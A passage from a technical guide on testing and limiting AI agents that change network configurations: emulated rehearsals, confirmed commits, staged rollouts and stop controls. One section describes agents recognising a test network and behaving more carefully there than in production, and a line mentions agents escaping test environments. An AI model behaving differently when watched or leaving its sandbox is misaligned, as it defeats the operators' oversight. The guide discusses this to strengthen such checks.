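    - endpoints: ["R1:eth1", "R2:eth1"]
```

A small company can afford an emulated network. Krentsel and colleagues ran 60 virtual Arista routers on one server with 128 GB of memory, and 1,000 on a cluster of 17 machines. Some emulated networks don't run router vendors' software, though. NetArena's routing tasks ran in Mininet with Linux commands, so they could not have revealed a quirk of a Cisco or Juniper router.

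A digital twin is a copy that software keeps synchronized with the production network. Some twins run device software, and others are databases that feed a simulator. A physical laboratory contains real devices, usually only a few of each type because they are expensive.

| Test network | What it can reveal | What it usually misses |
|---|---|---|
| Simulator | Wrong routes, overloaded links, the effects of many possible failures | Anything its model leaves out, including software bugs |
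| Emulated network | Rejected commands, vendors' quirks, short outages during a change | Faulty hardware, the effects of heavy traffic |
| Digital twin | Conflicts with the network as it is today | Depends on whether it simulates or emulates |
| Physical laboratory | Hardware faults, real forwarding speeds | Problems that appear only in a large network |

### A rehearsal on four routers

Suppose technicians have to replace the cable between R1 and R2 tonight, and an operator asks an agent to take that link out of service. This should be safe, because the offices can reach everything else through R3. A rehearsal tests whether the offices can in fact do so and whether the agent checks this before taking the link down.

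1. **Copy the current state.** Software fetches the running configurations, software versions and cabling map, replaces the passwords and keys, and starts virtual copies of the routers and the firewall. Small stand-in machines represent the offices, the payment servers, the internet provider and the bank.
2. **Test the invariants.** If one fails here but holds in production, the copy is wrong and the rehearsal stops.
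3. **Inject a fault.** The operator switches off the link between R3 and R4 without telling the agent. All the invariants still hold, because the offices' traffic goes through R2.
4. **Apply the change.** The agent logs in to R1 and switches off its link to R2.
5. **Wait for convergence.** Software waits until the forwarding tables on all routers have stopped changing and OSPF's 40-second timer has run out.
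6. **Test the invariants again.**
7. **Undo the change, wait, and test once more.** Software also compares the configurations and routes with those from the second step.

Without the injected fault, every test passes. With it, the results look like this:

| Invariant | Before the change | After the change | After undoing it |
|---|---|---|---|
| The offices can reach the payment servers | Pass | Fail | Pass |
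| The offices can reach the internet | Pass | Fail | Pass |
| The offices can open SSH sessions to R2 and R4 | Pass | Fail | Pass |
| The payment servers can reach the bank | Pass | Pass | Pass |

A careful agent would have looked at R3's neighbours, found that R4 was missing and refused to switch off the other link. The operator learns that this agent doesn't check the spare path, and can add the check to the procedure.

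The stand-in machines should also send each other packets throughout the rehearsal and count the losses, to catch short outages. These packets cover only a few of the possible connections, so Krentsel and colleagues copy the forwarding tables from the emulated routers into Batfish, which checks all possible packets. The vendors' software computes the routes, so Batfish does not have to predict them.

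An emulated copy of a 30-router part of Google's network took 12 to 17 minutes to start. The routers then needed about three minutes to settle, with millions of routes from each BGP neighbour. That is fast enough for planned maintenance, but during an outage an operator would want a copy that is already running.

The way the agent connects can make a change look safer in rehearsal than it is. Emulators usually give each virtual device a separate management link to the server it runs on, and an agent that logs in over that link cannot lock itself out. In production, the agent would reach the routers through the network it is changing, so the operator should run the agent's SSH sessions from the stand-in office machine.

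If the offices lose their internet connection, an agent whose model runs on another company's servers cannot reach the model, so it cannot undo the change. The rehearsal reveals this problem only if the operator also cuts the agent's connection to the model when the emulated internet link fails.

### When undoing a change does not undo it

The last step of the rehearsal can matter even when a change is as simple as switching something off and on again. *Crescent* (Gao, Abhashkumar and colleagues, 2024) describes an incident at ByteDance, TikTok's parent company, in which such a change went wrong.

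To move traffic away from a switch temporarily, an operator disabled a BGP peer group (a set of neighbours that share the same settings) and later re-enabled it. On that vendor's equipment, disabling the group also deleted the configuration lines that assigned neighbours to it, and re-enabling the group did not restore them.

One of the group's settings made routes through the switch look longer than they were. A neighbour that had lost the setting offered a route that looked shorter than the others. BGP generally prefers shorter routes, so all the traffic moved to a single link and congested it.

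A ping test would probably have passed, because the destinations were still reachable. Comparing the routes before and after the change would have revealed the difference, but only if the test network ran that vendor's software. An agent could easily make the same mistake, since "disable" and "enable" sound like exact opposites.

### CrystalNet and its successors

Engineers have long tested changes on small emulated networks. Microsoft researchers Liu, Zhu and colleagues (2017) proposed a much larger emulation in *CrystalNet*. They would test all network operations in advance on a copy of the company's production network, built from virtual machines in the cloud.

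Emulating every device is expensive, so CrystalNet could emulate only the part of the network around a change and leave out the devices beyond a boundary. This is safe only if the change cannot set off a reaction outside the boundary that would affect the devices inside it.

Microsoft's later system is the Open Network Emulator. Lee (2019) describes a copy of about 5,000 routers on which engineers ran a migration step by step, reset the network when a step failed, and tried another approach. Lee credits the emulator with helping Microsoft complete all its major migrations without affecting customers. By 2022 the company used more than 30 million core-hours a year on emulation, according to Tantsura (2022). That equals about 3,400 processor cores running day and night.

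Gao and colleagues examined roughly 100 incidents on ByteDance's network over three years and found that CrystalNet's method of choosing a boundary would not have been safe there. The method could have missed about 60% of the incidents caused by changes. In one case, a change on one router made distant routers from another vendor drop a route, because the vendors applied a rule against routing loops differently. A copy of only the changed router and its immediate surroundings would have left out those distant routers.

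ByteDance's emulator, Crescent, always includes all the core devices, where more than 90% of these incidents began, and a sample of the others. Data centres contain many switches with nearly identical configurations, so one switch can represent many. Crescent therefore emulates less than 2% of the company's devices. A company with less uniform switch configurations would need to emulate a larger share.

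About a third of ByteDance's incidents came from changes, and 30% of those involved behaviour specific to one vendor. That is only about ten cases, but they are the kind that configuration analysis is most likely to miss. Incidents per thousand changes fell steadily after ByteDance introduced Crescent in late 2020, and further after it became mandatory for critical changes in mid-2022. Other improvements over those years may have contributed.

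### Swisscom's change that passed the laboratory

Outshift, Cisco's incubation group, reports that a routine configuration change at Swisscom passed all the standard laboratory tests and then disrupted the production network. Outshift argues that physical laboratories are slow and expensive and cannot fully reproduce a live network.

After the outage, Swisscom and Outshift built a system of AI agents that tests proposed changes on a digital twin. When they gave it the change that had caused the outage, the change failed the tests, and the results identified the faulty setting. After they corrected the setting, the change passed all the tests.

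This is a single case reported by the system's developer, and everyone involved already knew the change was faulty. The result would be stronger evidence if the system had also judged a few hundred ordinary changes, because people will soon stop using a tool that rejects too many good changes.

Swisscom's twin may also not be an emulated network. ZenML's *Multi-Agent AI System for Network Change Management* (2025) describes an Outshift system that keeps configurations and measurements from the production network in a database. One agent reads the change ticket and coordinates the others, which assess the impact, write a test plan and run the tests with tools such as Batfish. If Swisscom's twin works this way, it computes what the routers should do without running their software. It could cover far more of the network than a laboratory, but it would miss the same problems as other configuration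 analysis.

### Microsoft's outage of January 2023

Microsoft had a large emulator and required engineers to use it, but an untested command still caused a worldwide outage. On 25 January 2023, an engineer was adding capacity to the company's wide-area network in Madrid. The work included changing the addresses of new routers and connecting them to the routing protocols.

Microsoft (2023) sets out the four steps that its standard procedure requires for such work:

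1. Test the change in the emulator.
2. Test it in the physical laboratory.
3. Have colleagues review both results and the plans for making and undoing the change.
4. Make the change with access to one device at a time.

Somebody had edited the procedure to fix problems from earlier uses, but the new version was untested and contained an extra command to clear the routing protocol's database. On routers from two of Microsoft's suppliers, the command clears only the local router's database. On the Madrid router, from a third supplier, it made every router in the wide-area network recompute its routes.

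While they did so, the routers could not forward packets correctly. Users around the world lost access to Teams, Outlook and other services, and the network took about an hour and 40 minutes to restore every route. Some services did not recover until the afternoon.

Two other safeguards failed. A central server checked each command against a list of blocked ones, but this command was not on the list because Microsoft had not realised that it had a global effect on this router model. Limiting the command to one device did not help because the router passed the instruction on to the other routers. Monitoring alerted the on-call engineers within five minutes, but nobody told the engineer in Madrid, who ran the same command on a second router 33 minutes after the first.

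A rehearsal would probably have caught the problem, but only if the test network included software from the third supplier and at least one other router to receive the instruction, and only if a test ran during the change. A small network recomputes its routes in moments and ends up as it was before, so a check after convergence would have found nothing wrong. Packet counts, or a log entry on a router that nobody had touched, would have revealed the effect.

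An agent is more likely to create this kind of gap between what was tested and what is run. The engineer in Madrid followed a written procedure that had changed once, but an agent may write slightly different commands every time. If any edit invalidates the earlier test, as it should have at Microsoft, every new draft needs its own rehearsal.

### What the copy leaves out

Emulated networks carry little traffic, so they rarely reveal congestion. Gao and colleagues describe a case that Crescent missed. A router with several equally good links chooses one for each connection by a calculation on the packet's addresses. If the next router uses the same calculation, it can send most of the connections it receives over one link and leave the others nearly empty. Every connection still works in the test, so the problem appears only when production traffic overloads that link.

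Emulation also leaves out the hardware. Krentsel and colleagues describe a router whose forwarding chip did not store the entries its software had computed. An emulator runs only the software, which would have appeared healthy.

Some bugs appear only at the scale of the production network. In October 2020, one such bug, in an update to the software that directs traffic between Microsoft's regions, congested some routes. Microsoft responded by testing such software in the emulator for longer and by injecting bursts of random failures to make rare problems more common.

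Testing random failures covers only a small part of what can go wrong. A network with 1,000 links has 499,500 pairs of links that could fail together, and at one minute per pair, a single emulated copy would need almost a year to test them all. Simulators are better suited to such searches. ByteDance instead injects failures into the critical parts of its emulated network at regular intervals. These tests found a border device that lacked a setting and would have caused a routing loop if particular links had failed.

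When the outcome depends on the order of messages, one run of an emulated network produces only one of the possible results, as Batfish does. But an operator can run the same rehearsal on several copies at once and investigate if the results differ. This will still usually miss bugs that take weeks of operation to appear.

The emulator can also introduce its own faults. In one of ByteDance's virtual devices, a program that identifies neighbouring equipment crashed repeatedly because the device had too many ports, and the crash logs filled the server's memory. An agent that found such a fault might try to repair a problem that did not exist in production.

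### What a rehearsal shows about the agent

An operator can rehearse either a specific set of commands or the agent's ability to write them. A successful rehearsal of specific commands is good evidence only if the live network receives the same commands. An agent that starts the task again on the live network may write different ones, so the policy gate should save the rehearsed text and send exactly that.

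Saving the commands from a rehearsal doesn't work for fault-finding, because the agent has to choose each step after it reads the last result. The operator needs many rehearsals with different faults, and should study the record of each run as well as its result. For example, the operator should look at whether the agent checked the spare path, whether it waited for convergence before judging a test, and whether it stopped when a command failed or tried something more drastic.

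The faults and addresses should vary, because otherwise an agent may do well by recalling memorised answers. For this reason, Zhou and colleagues generate new faults at random, hide them from the agent, and accept any repair that restores the healthy network. In NetConfArena, Liu and colleagues hide both the reference answer and the tests.

The test network should hold about as much configuration as the real one. Bracciale and colleagues estimate that a production backbone or data centre has between 100,000 and a million configuration items, and they say that conflicts between these items cause collateral damage. In a clean laboratory with four routers and one service, an agent can reuse an identifier or change a global setting without harming anything. Bracciale and colleagues used a test network with about ten kinds of service, each with thousands of items.

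The agent also needs the same tools in the laboratory as in production. Bracciale and colleagues cite OperAID, a benchmark for agents that repair mobile networks, in which access to more read-only tools raised an agent's success rate from 11% to 61%. A laboratory with better monitoring than the real network would therefore make the agent look more capable than it would be on that network.

### If the model recognises the test

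An AI agent can recognize a test network from details in the equipment's output. The routers may show an uptime of four minutes, the traffic counters may be near zero, and the hardware model may contain the word "virtual". Language models are trained on a great deal of material about laboratories and benchmarks, and some write in their reasoning that they seem to be in a test.

If a rehearsal looks like a test to the agent, the result can be distorted in either direction. The agent may check its work more thoroughly than usual, because training often rewards models for passing tests. Or it may take more risks, because restarting a router in a laboratory harms nobody and is often the quickest repair. The first case is more dangerous for an operator, since the agent would look safer in rehearsals than it is on live equipment.

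Operators can remove the most obvious signs that a network is emulated by loading old logs, generating background traffic, letting the routers run for a few days, and using the production names for devices and tools. They can also measure how much the description of the network affects the agent by giving it the same task on the same emulated network several times, calling the network a laboratory in half of the runs and production in the other half. If the agent skips its checks in only one half, the rehearsals are poor evidence of how it will behave in production.

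A lack of difference between the halves is reassuring but inconclusive, because the model may have recognised the laboratory in both. The permissions and gates around the agent should therefore stay in place however well it does in rehearsals.

### Why the laboratory needs its own credentials

A good copy of a production network contains the same names, addresses and keys, so it can interfere with the real network if the two are connected. At ByteDance, the container software had given an emulated device a default route to the outside, and the device sent its log messages to the production log server. The server could not distinguish the copy from the real device and reported many failed links. Engineers spent a lot of time finding the cause of these false alarms.

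Worse accidents are possible. A copy of R2 with the real BGP settings might connect to the company's actual internet provider and announce routes to it. A copy of R4 has the same address as the real R4, so if the agent's machine can reach both, a command meant for the copy may restart the real R4 in the data centre.

The operator can prevent this with several separate barriers:

- The laboratory has no route to production devices, controllers, log servers or login servers.
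- The agent uses laboratory accounts and keys that production devices reject.
- Software replaces the keys and passwords in copied configurations before the virtual routers start.
- If the agent needs an outside model, it reaches the model through one relay that connects to nothing else.

Engineers should test these barriers by trying to reach production from the laboratory. They should also try from inside a virtual router, since an agent with a shell there might find a path to production that is not available from its own machine. Instructing an agent to stay inside the laboratory is not enough, because AI agents left test environments and got into other systems in 2026.

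### Read-only access and shadow operation

After laboratory testing, the agent can diagnose real faults on the production network through a read-only account, and engineers can later compare its answers with the causes they found. This exposes the agent to conditions that laboratories rarely include, such as misleading device names, outdated documentation and settings that nobody remembers adding. Read-only access can still leak secrets, overload devices and expose the agent to planted instructions.

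The next step is shadow operation. For each real job, the agent receives the same request as the engineer and writes a complete proposal, but no device receives it. The engineer does the job as usual, and the team then compares the agent's proposal with what the engineer did.

The comparison is harder than it sounds. Suppose the job is again to take the link between R1 and R2 out of service:

```
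Engineer                            Agent
R1: raise the cost towards R2       R1: switch off the link to R2
R2: raise the cost towards R1       R2: switch off the link to R1
R1: switch off the link to R2
```

One way to compare them is the configuration score that Liu and colleagues use in NetConfArena alongside their tests of behaviour. Precision is the share of the agent's changes that also appear in the reference, and recall is the share of the reference that the agent reproduced. The score, F1, combines them:

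```
precision = 1/2      recall = 1/3

F1 = 2 × precision × recall / (precision + recall) = 0.4
```

The score of 0.4 out of 1 is misleadingly low, because both versions leave the traffic on the same paths. Comparing only the final routes would also be misleading, because the engineer moved the traffic away before switching off the link, whereas the agent's version would have dropped packets until the routers found the other path. To measure that difference, the team has to run both versions in the emulated network and count the lost packets.

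The engineer's version of a change isn't always better than the agent's, so a third person should review the disagreements without knowing who wrote which. The agent needs a snapshot of the network from before the engineer started work, because otherwise it may copy the engineer's answer. Engineers should not see the agent's proposal until they have finished, because they might adopt it, which would make the agreement meaningless.

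Most jobs in any month are routine, and a high rate of agreement on port descriptions and user moves is weak evidence of how the agent would handle routing changes. The team should therefore count results separately for each kind of job. Rare and dangerous jobs may not come up during a few months of shadow operation, so rehearsals remain the main evidence for them.

Shadow operation also doesn't test what the agent does after its own commands reach a device, such as whether it repeats a request that timed out or leaves a job half finished when the third of four routers stops responding. The agent can practise these situations in the laboratory, but it won't face them in production until it starts changing a few devices there.

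## Timed rollback and staged deployment

Some of an agent's mistakes will get past the analysis and the rehearsals and reach production devices. With a timed rollback, a device restores its old configuration unless it receives a confirmation in time, which limits how long a mistake lasts. In a staged deployment, the agent changes a few devices and tests them before it continues, so a mistake can be caught before it is repeated on the rest. Both methods fail if the tests miss the fault. Staged deployment also gives little protection when one device, such as a router with a wrong routing policy, can disrupt the whole network.

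### The confirmed commit, step by step

NETCONF's timed rollback is the confirmed commit. Enns (2011), in *Network Configuration Protocol (NETCONF)*, describes how a program can use it to change one device:

1. Lock the running and candidate configurations, so that nobody else can edit them.
2. Save a copy of the running configuration.
3. Load the change into the candidate configuration and ask the device to validate it.
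4. Commit the candidate with a timer.
5. Test the network.
6. Send a second, ordinary commit to keep the change. If a test fails, cancel the first commit or let the timer run out.
7. Release the locks.

The request in the fourth step looks like this:

```
<commit>
  <confirmed/>
  <confirm-timeout>120</confirm-timeout>
</commit>
```

The timeout is in seconds and defaults to 600 if the request omits it. If the program skips the locks, a rollback can also remove a change a colleague made in the same few minutes.

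The name "confirmed commit" is confusing because the commit still needs confirming. The RFC Editor's *RFC Errata* includes a 2013 proposal to state this in the standard. A model that interprets "confirmed" in its usual sense might treat the job as finished.

The device also restores the old configuration if it restarts or if the session that sent the commit ends. This is useful when the agent program crashes, but a correct change can also end the session. Hansford's *Is there a problem with confirmed commits?* (2019) gives the example of changing the device's own IP address. The program can add a `persist` token to the commit so that the change survives the end of the session. Any later session that supplies the token can then confirm or cancel the change. Devices that support only the first version of the confirmed commit have neither the token nor the cancel operation.

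### A lockout that ends by itself

Suppose R3 is a Juniper router, and an agent in the offices adds a filter that limits who can connect to the router itself. The filter permits OSPF and a monitoring server in the data centre, but the agent mistakenly leaves out a rule permitting logins from the offices.

| Time | Event | Can the offices log in to R3? |
|---|---|---|
| 22:00:00 | The agent locks the configurations and loads the filter | Yes |
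| 22:00:04 | R3 validates the filter and finds no errors | Yes |
| 22:00:05 | The agent commits with a 120-second timer, and R3 replies "ok" | No |
| 22:00:15 | A test program in the offices tries to log in and gets no answer | No |
| 22:00:45 | The test fails, and the agent tries to cancel the commit, but R3 drops the request | No |
| 22:02:05 | The timer runs out, and R3 restores the old configuration | Yes |
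| 22:02:15 | The test program logs in | Yes |

The agent receives the "ok" because the filter checks only incoming packets. R3 cannot distinguish a blocked agent from a waiting one, so it does not detect that the session is dead. Users notice nothing, because the filter doesn't apply to traffic that passes through R3.

The length of the timer is a compromise:

```
timer            >  slowest fault to appear + time to test + time to confirm
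longest lockout  ≈  timer + time for routes to settle again
```

The timer has to be longer than 80 seconds to cover OSPF's 40-second limit, 30 seconds of tests and 10 seconds to confirm, so 120 seconds is enough. By default, a Cisco router waits 180 seconds before declaring a silent BGP neighbour down, which raises the minimum to 220 seconds. The standard's 600 seconds covers both cases, but a lockout would last ten minutes with that setting.

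### Junos, Cisco and the scheduled reload

The command lines of the main vendors have their own versions:

| Equipment | Start the timer | Keep the change | Time allowed |
|---|---|---|---|
| Juniper Junos | `commit confirmed 2` | `commit` or `commit check` | 10 minutes by default |
| Cisco IOS | `configure terminal revert timer 2` | `configure confirm` | The user must set it |
| Cisco IOS XR | `commit confirmed 120` | `commit` | 30 to 65,535 seconds |
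| Scheduled reload on Cisco IOS | `reload in 5` | `reload cancel` | The user must set it |

The range for IOS XR comes from the University of Cologne's *IOS XR reload in 10*.

On Junos, `commit check` normally only checks a draft for errors. But Juniper also lists it as a way to confirm a pending commit, so an agent that runs it as a precaution can make a faulty change permanent. An agent can also delay the rollback. According to Juniper's *Commit the Candidate Configuration Only After Confirmation Using NETCONF*, each new confirmed commit restarts the timer, which can be set to at most 4,294,967,295 seconds, or about 136 years. The policy gate should therefore set the timer and limit the number of extensions.

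Cisco's traditional routers apply each line as it arrives, so the rollback timer has to start before the first line. With a two-minute timer, R4 would have recovered from the access-list lockout without help. Cisco's *Configuration Replace and Configuration Rollback* (2011) explains that, to roll back, the router compares the running configuration with a saved copy and applies only the differences. In very rare cases, the router cannot remove a command without a restart. The guide also warns that copying a saved file into the running configuration merges the two, so an agent that tries to undo its work this way leaves its new lines in place.

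A scheduled reload is a crude substitute for timed rollback. Williams, a Cisco employee, describes saving the working configuration, entering `reload in 5`, making the change, and cancelling the reload if everything works. If the change locks the user out, the router restarts and loads the saved configuration. The restart interrupts all traffic through the router for several minutes, and it doesn't restore the working configuration if the agent has already saved the faulty one.

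The `reload in` command can also mean different things on different equipment. On Nexus 9000 switches, `reload in 15` means 15 seconds, not minutes, and the switch restarts without asking for confirmation, according to a Cisco defect notice that BugZero reproduces. An agent that learned the command on a router could restart a data-centre switch before making any changes.

### What RESTCONF offers instead

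Standard RESTCONF has no confirmed commit, so a successful edit stays until somebody reverses it. The standard (Bierman et al.) requires a device with a separate startup configuration to save every RESTCONF edit there automatically, so a scheduled reload would not undo the edit either.

A RESTCONF edit can confirm another client's pending commit. This happens on devices where edits must pass through a candidate configuration, because the device commits the candidate after each RESTCONF edit. Suppose the agent on R3 had skipped the locks. At 22:01, the monitoring server, which the new filter still admits, uses RESTCONF to update a port's description. R3 commits the description, treats that commit as the missing confirmation and stops the timer, so the offices stay locked out.

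Locks prevent this because the device must refuse the RESTCONF edit with "409 Conflict" while they are held. It must also refuse the edit if the pending commit has a `persist` token. An agent should use both, since the device releases the locks when the session ends but still requires the token.

Some vendors add a timer of their own. YumaWorks' *How to use the confirmed commit procedure in RESTCONF* describes an extension in its server software:

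```
PATCH /restconf/data?confirmed=1&confirm-timeout=30&persist=abcde
```

A standard RESTCONF device without the extension should reject the unrecognized parameters, but a less strict controller might ignore them and apply the change permanently.

### How the safeguard fails

The simplest failure is that the agent confirms too early. It reads "ok", concludes that the change worked and sends the second commit a few seconds later. The timer then protects only against an immediate lockout.

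An agent may also test only its own connection. The faulty route filter drafted for R2, for example, would have cut the bank off from the payment servers while the agent's session kept working. A test from a machine outside the company would have caught this. The test program on R3 opened a new session because some firewalls let existing connections continue after a rule change and block only new ones, so an agent that stays logged in can miss a lockout.

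Software separate from the agent should therefore run the tests and control confirmation of the commit. Junos Space, a management platform from Juniper, works roughly this way. It sends a confirmed commit, calls a separate check, and confirms only if the check returns "true" before the timer ends. Otherwise, the device goes back to its old configuration. With NETCONF, the separate software can send the commit itself and withhold the `persist` token from the agent.

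A timed rollback can't catch a fault that appears after the timer has ended, however good the tests are. For example, a change made at night may not overload a link until people start work in the morning. At Rogers, the full outage began after a standard ten-minute timer would have ended. The test software should therefore keep running after the change is confirmed, and the operator should keep the saved copy of the configuration. A late reversal restores the configuration but not everything the network has lost in the meantime.

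### When several devices have to go back together

Timers on separate devices can leave them in different states. Suppose software installs a new OSPF key on all four office routers, using a confirmed commit with a 120-second timer on each. The tests pass and it sends four confirmations, but the one for R4 gets lost:

| Time | R1, R2 and R3 | R4 | Can the payment servers reach the bank? |
|---|---|---|---|
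| 22:00:00 | New key, timer running | New key, timer running | Yes |
| 22:01:30 | New key, confirmed | New key, timer running | Yes |
| 22:02:00 | New key | Old key | Yes, for up to 40 seconds |
| 22:02:40 | New key | Old key, no OSPF neighbours | No |

Every router followed the standard, and the rollback on R4 caused the outage. The software has already confirmed the commits on the other three routers, so it can no longer cancel them and needs the saved copies to restore the old key. It should therefore keep all the copies and locks until every device has acknowledged its confirmation. It should also start confirming early enough to resend a lost message.

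Enns calls a complete all-or-nothing guarantee across devices "prohibitively expensive", but suggests carrying out each step on all devices in parallel to shorten the periods in which a failure can leave them in different states. Some changes don't need such a guarantee. If an agent adds a time server to 50 routers and the change fails on three, it can retry those three the next day. A customer's private network, by contrast, may need matching settings on every router it uses.

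The ANI-Gamut runs combined rollback with other features, so it is still unclear how much rollback itself improves an agent's results. Bracciale and colleagues plan to test prevention and recovery separately.

### A thousand switches in four waves

Suppose a company has 1,000 office switches and wants an agent to turn on a protection for DHCP, the service that gives machines their network addresses. A visitor's misconfigured laptop can hand out wrong addresses, so the new setting makes each switch drop DHCP replies unless they arrive on a port marked as trusted. The agent marks the port that normally connects the switch to the rest of the network. On 50 older switches, that connection uses a different port and nobody remembers this, so those switches will drop replies from the company's real DHCP server.

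A confirmed commit with a ten-minute timer probably wouldn't catch the fault, because machines that already have an address can keep it for hours. The test has to include a machine that requests a new address.

The agent changes the switches in waves of 1, 10, 100 and 889, and the test runs on every switch after each wave. If software picks the switches at random, the chance that a wave of n contains at least one of the 50 is about 1 − 0.95ⁿ:

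| Switches in the wave | Chance that the wave reveals the fault | Faulty switches to expect |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | 5% | 0.05 |
| 10 | 40% | 0.5 |
| 100 | 99% | 5 |
| 889 | Almost certain | 44 |

The deployment will almost certainly stop by the third wave, with about five offices affected instead of 50. Even if all 111 switches in the first three waves had passed, a rarer fault could still exist. Under the rule of three, which Bracciale and colleagues use to plan their tests, the upper 95% limit on the failure rate after n successes and no failures is about 3/n. For 111 switches, that limit is 2.7%, or 24 of the remaining 889 switches. The software should therefore split the last wave into batches too, and stop when one fails.

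These numbers hold only if the switches are chosen at random. An agent that takes the first ten switches on a list may get ten identical ones from the same building. The early waves should also include every model and software version, and no wave should contain both switches of a redundant pair.

Bilal and colleagues count the rules for staged rollout and rollback among the gates that an agent must not bypass. Software outside the model should therefore fix the list of devices in advance and decide when the next wave of changes starts. Before its maintenance in California in July 2026, Microsoft checked that at least one of two redundant paths would stay up. According to Cooter (2026), in *Microsoft’s Californian outage*, this check had not covered the routes that disappeared when the automation selected extra devices. A gate that compared the selected devices with the planned list could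 have blocked the job.

### When a few devices do not predict the rest

Deploying in waves works for the DHCP setting because each switch affects only its own users. A router's policy affects everyone who receives its routes, so even a first wave of one router can cause a large outage. Cloudflare's leak in January came from a single router in Miami. The failure that grounded US flights in November began at one site in Arkansas. TechSpot's *Two routers that couldn't work together disrupted 18,000 US flights* (2026) reports that the failure stopped nearly all departures for about five hours. The contractor said the incompatibility behind it had not caused trouble before.

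A change can also be harmless on a few devices and harmful on many. Suppose a change makes each of 1,000 branch routers announce 500 extra routes, and the core routers have room for 100,000 more. After the first three waves, the branches announce 55,500 extra routes and every test passes. The core routers run out of room at the 200th branch router, early in the last wave, and the branches the agent hasn't changed lose service too.

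For changes like these, configuration analysis and rehearsal have to provide most of the evidence that the change is safe before the first device changes. Limits on the number of routes each neighbour accepts can contain some of the mistakes that analysis and rehearsal miss. The tests after each wave should check the routes that neighbours receive and the spare capacity of shared devices, as well as the devices the agent has changed.

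### Limiting the pace

An agent can make many changes before a person notices the first mistake. *Governance Framework for AI-Mediated Autonomous Network Device Management* (Smith and Pai, 2026), which is not a standard, proposes a default limit of five repair actions an hour and a maximum of 20. For any one interface or neighbour, the default is three a day. The agent would have to calculate these limits from a stored log, so that restarting the agent doesn't reset the count.

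Such limits suit unplanned repairs. At 20 actions an hour, the DHCP change would take 50 hours, so a planned deployment needs its own limit. The proposal also assumes that each agent looks after one device. If 1,000 devices each have an agent, the agents could together make 5,000 changes an hour, perhaps all in response to the same fault. An operator therefore needs a limit for the whole network. This limit should count devices rather than requests, because one request to a controller can change all the devices.

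Smith and Pai also forbid repairs while routes are settling. Their agent pauses when at least two critical signs of instability, such as a lost BGP neighbour and a burst of route updates, appear in the same round of measurements. This would prevent the agent from reacting to a test that fails during a brief routing loop. Read strictly, the rule would also stop the agent from undoing a change that caused the instability, so an operator should exempt rollbacks. A rollback timer already running on a device continues even while the agent is paused.

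### Out-of-band access

A device that doesn't restore itself needs a second way for engineers to reach it, often a small console server that connects to the routers' serial ports and has its own mobile connection. That connection should use a different telecoms provider from the main network, and logins should work without the company's DNS or central login server. Engineers should log in through the console server regularly, because otherwise it may fail without anyone noticing until it is needed.

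The agent should not be able to change this path. Smith and Pai permanently protect management interfaces from any repair action, whatever the model recommends. They identify these interfaces partly by names that contain "mgmt", but also require a list from the operator because names vary.

A confirmation should use the normal path rather than the out-of-band path, so that it fails if the normal path is broken. In the lockout on R3, a program connected through the console server could have confirmed the change while the offices were still shut out. A cancellation, however, can use the out-of-band path, and on R3 this would have ended the lockout at 22:00:45 instead of 22:02:05. It requires a `persist` token because the request would come from a different session.

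### Stopping an agent halfway

Smith and Pai require that a person can stop an agent at any time, with immediate effect. They separate an emergency stop, which shuts the agent down, from a pause, which stops its repairs but leaves its monitoring on. On the network, the result of a stop depends on when it arrives:

| State of the job when the agent stops | What happens next |
|---|---|
| Edits in a locked candidate, not committed | The device discards them when the session ends |
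| Confirmed commit pending, no token | The device restores the old configuration when the session ends |
| Confirmed commit pending, with a token | The device restores the old configuration when the timer ends |
| Ordinary commits on two of four routers | Two routers keep the change and two never get it |
| Large job already sent to a controller | The controller carries on without the agent |

An agent that stops after changing the OSPF key on two routers leaves the network split. Smith and Pai avoid this by forbidding the agent to make any repair in which later steps depend on earlier ones. This restriction is safe, but it rules out much ordinary work, including moving traffic off a link before switching it off.

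An operator who allows such jobs should define a safe end for each in advance. For the key change, the safe end might be to restore the old key on every router if any of the four still lacks the new one, and to finish confirming if all four have it. For the DHCP setting, the switches can stay as they are if those already changed have passed their tests, because old and new settings work side by side.

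Separate software should carry out this plan, because the operator may have stopped the agent for behaving strangely. A stop would then work like this:

1. The gate refuses all further requests from the agent and closes its sessions.
2. The gate cancels any jobs the agent has sent to controllers.
3. The recovery software cancels pending commits, or finishes them if the plan says so.
4. It restores saved copies on devices where the agent has made permanent changes that the plan does not keep.
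5. It tests the invariants, releases any remaining locks and tells the engineers which devices differ from their state before the job.

The agent loses its authority in the first step, so clean-up doesn't delay stopping it. An engineer must also be able to halt the recovery software if it makes things worse. The operator can test the plan in an emulated network by running the same job repeatedly, stopping it after a different step each time, and checking the invariants on every run.

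## How much evidence should come before how much authority

An operator can limit an agent to reading, let it draft changes, let it carry out changes that a person has approved, or let it act alone. The higher levels of authority have the least evidence behind them. Bilal and colleagues found 13 evaluated systems that use language models for work on networks or cloud services. Only five could draft or make changes, and none went through the whole sequence of drafting a change, checking it independently, applying it and reversing it. How much testing an agent needs depends on the harm it could do. A few hundred clean runs may be enough for work on single ports, but they are weak evidence that an agent can safely change a core router.

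### Four levels and an assurance contract

Bilal and colleagues sort agents by the tools they may use, and propose stronger guarantees at each level:

| Level | What the agent may do | Main guarantees |
|---|---|---|
| Read-only assistant | Search and summarise | Each statement cites its source, and software removes secrets |
| Analyst | Also run diagnostic queries and suggest causes | The agent looks for contrary evidence and hands over to a person when unsure |
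| Write-limited planner | Also draft changes and carry out permitted kinds | Policy checks, invariants, staged deployment, a rollback plan and a signed record |
| Closed-loop controller | Find and repair faults continuously, within a narrow range | Automatic rollback, constant monitoring and regular audits |

They call the full set of conditions for a level its assurance contract. For the OSPF cost change on R1, a contract at the third level might contain this:

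```
Tools      read OSPF on all routers, draft a cost change, commit on R1
Evidence   current neighbours, link loads, paths before and after
Gates      all invariants hold, a person has approved this exact change
Rollout    confirmed commit with separate tests, full record kept
Budget     30 tool calls, 20 minutes, one device
```

A run meets the contract only if it meets every part, so it fails if the agent makes the right change but never compares the paths. The contract is a template, and Bilal and colleagues do not claim to have tested whether it reduces harm.

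The third level covers a wide range of authority, depending on who approves each change. Zhang and colleagues use a scale from C0 to C4 to separate these cases in their survey of autonomous networking. At C0, people choose and approve every significant action. At C1, the agent proposes actions and a person approves them. At C2, the agent handles routine jobs alone and passes unusual ones to a person. At C3, it works without individual approvals across a broader range of jobs. At C4, the network governs itself within declared limits.

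Bilal and colleagues also say that an agent at any level must stop and ask when two drafts pass all the checks but send traffic along different paths. In the job on R1, for example, the agent could raise the OSPF cost, which also moves the offices' web traffic, or add a fixed route that moves only the data-centre traffic. If the invariants cover only reachability, both drafts pass, and the operator has to choose between them.

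For deciding which changes need more scrutiny, they suggest a score:

```
risk = α × blast radius + β × novelty + γ × (1 − coverage)
```

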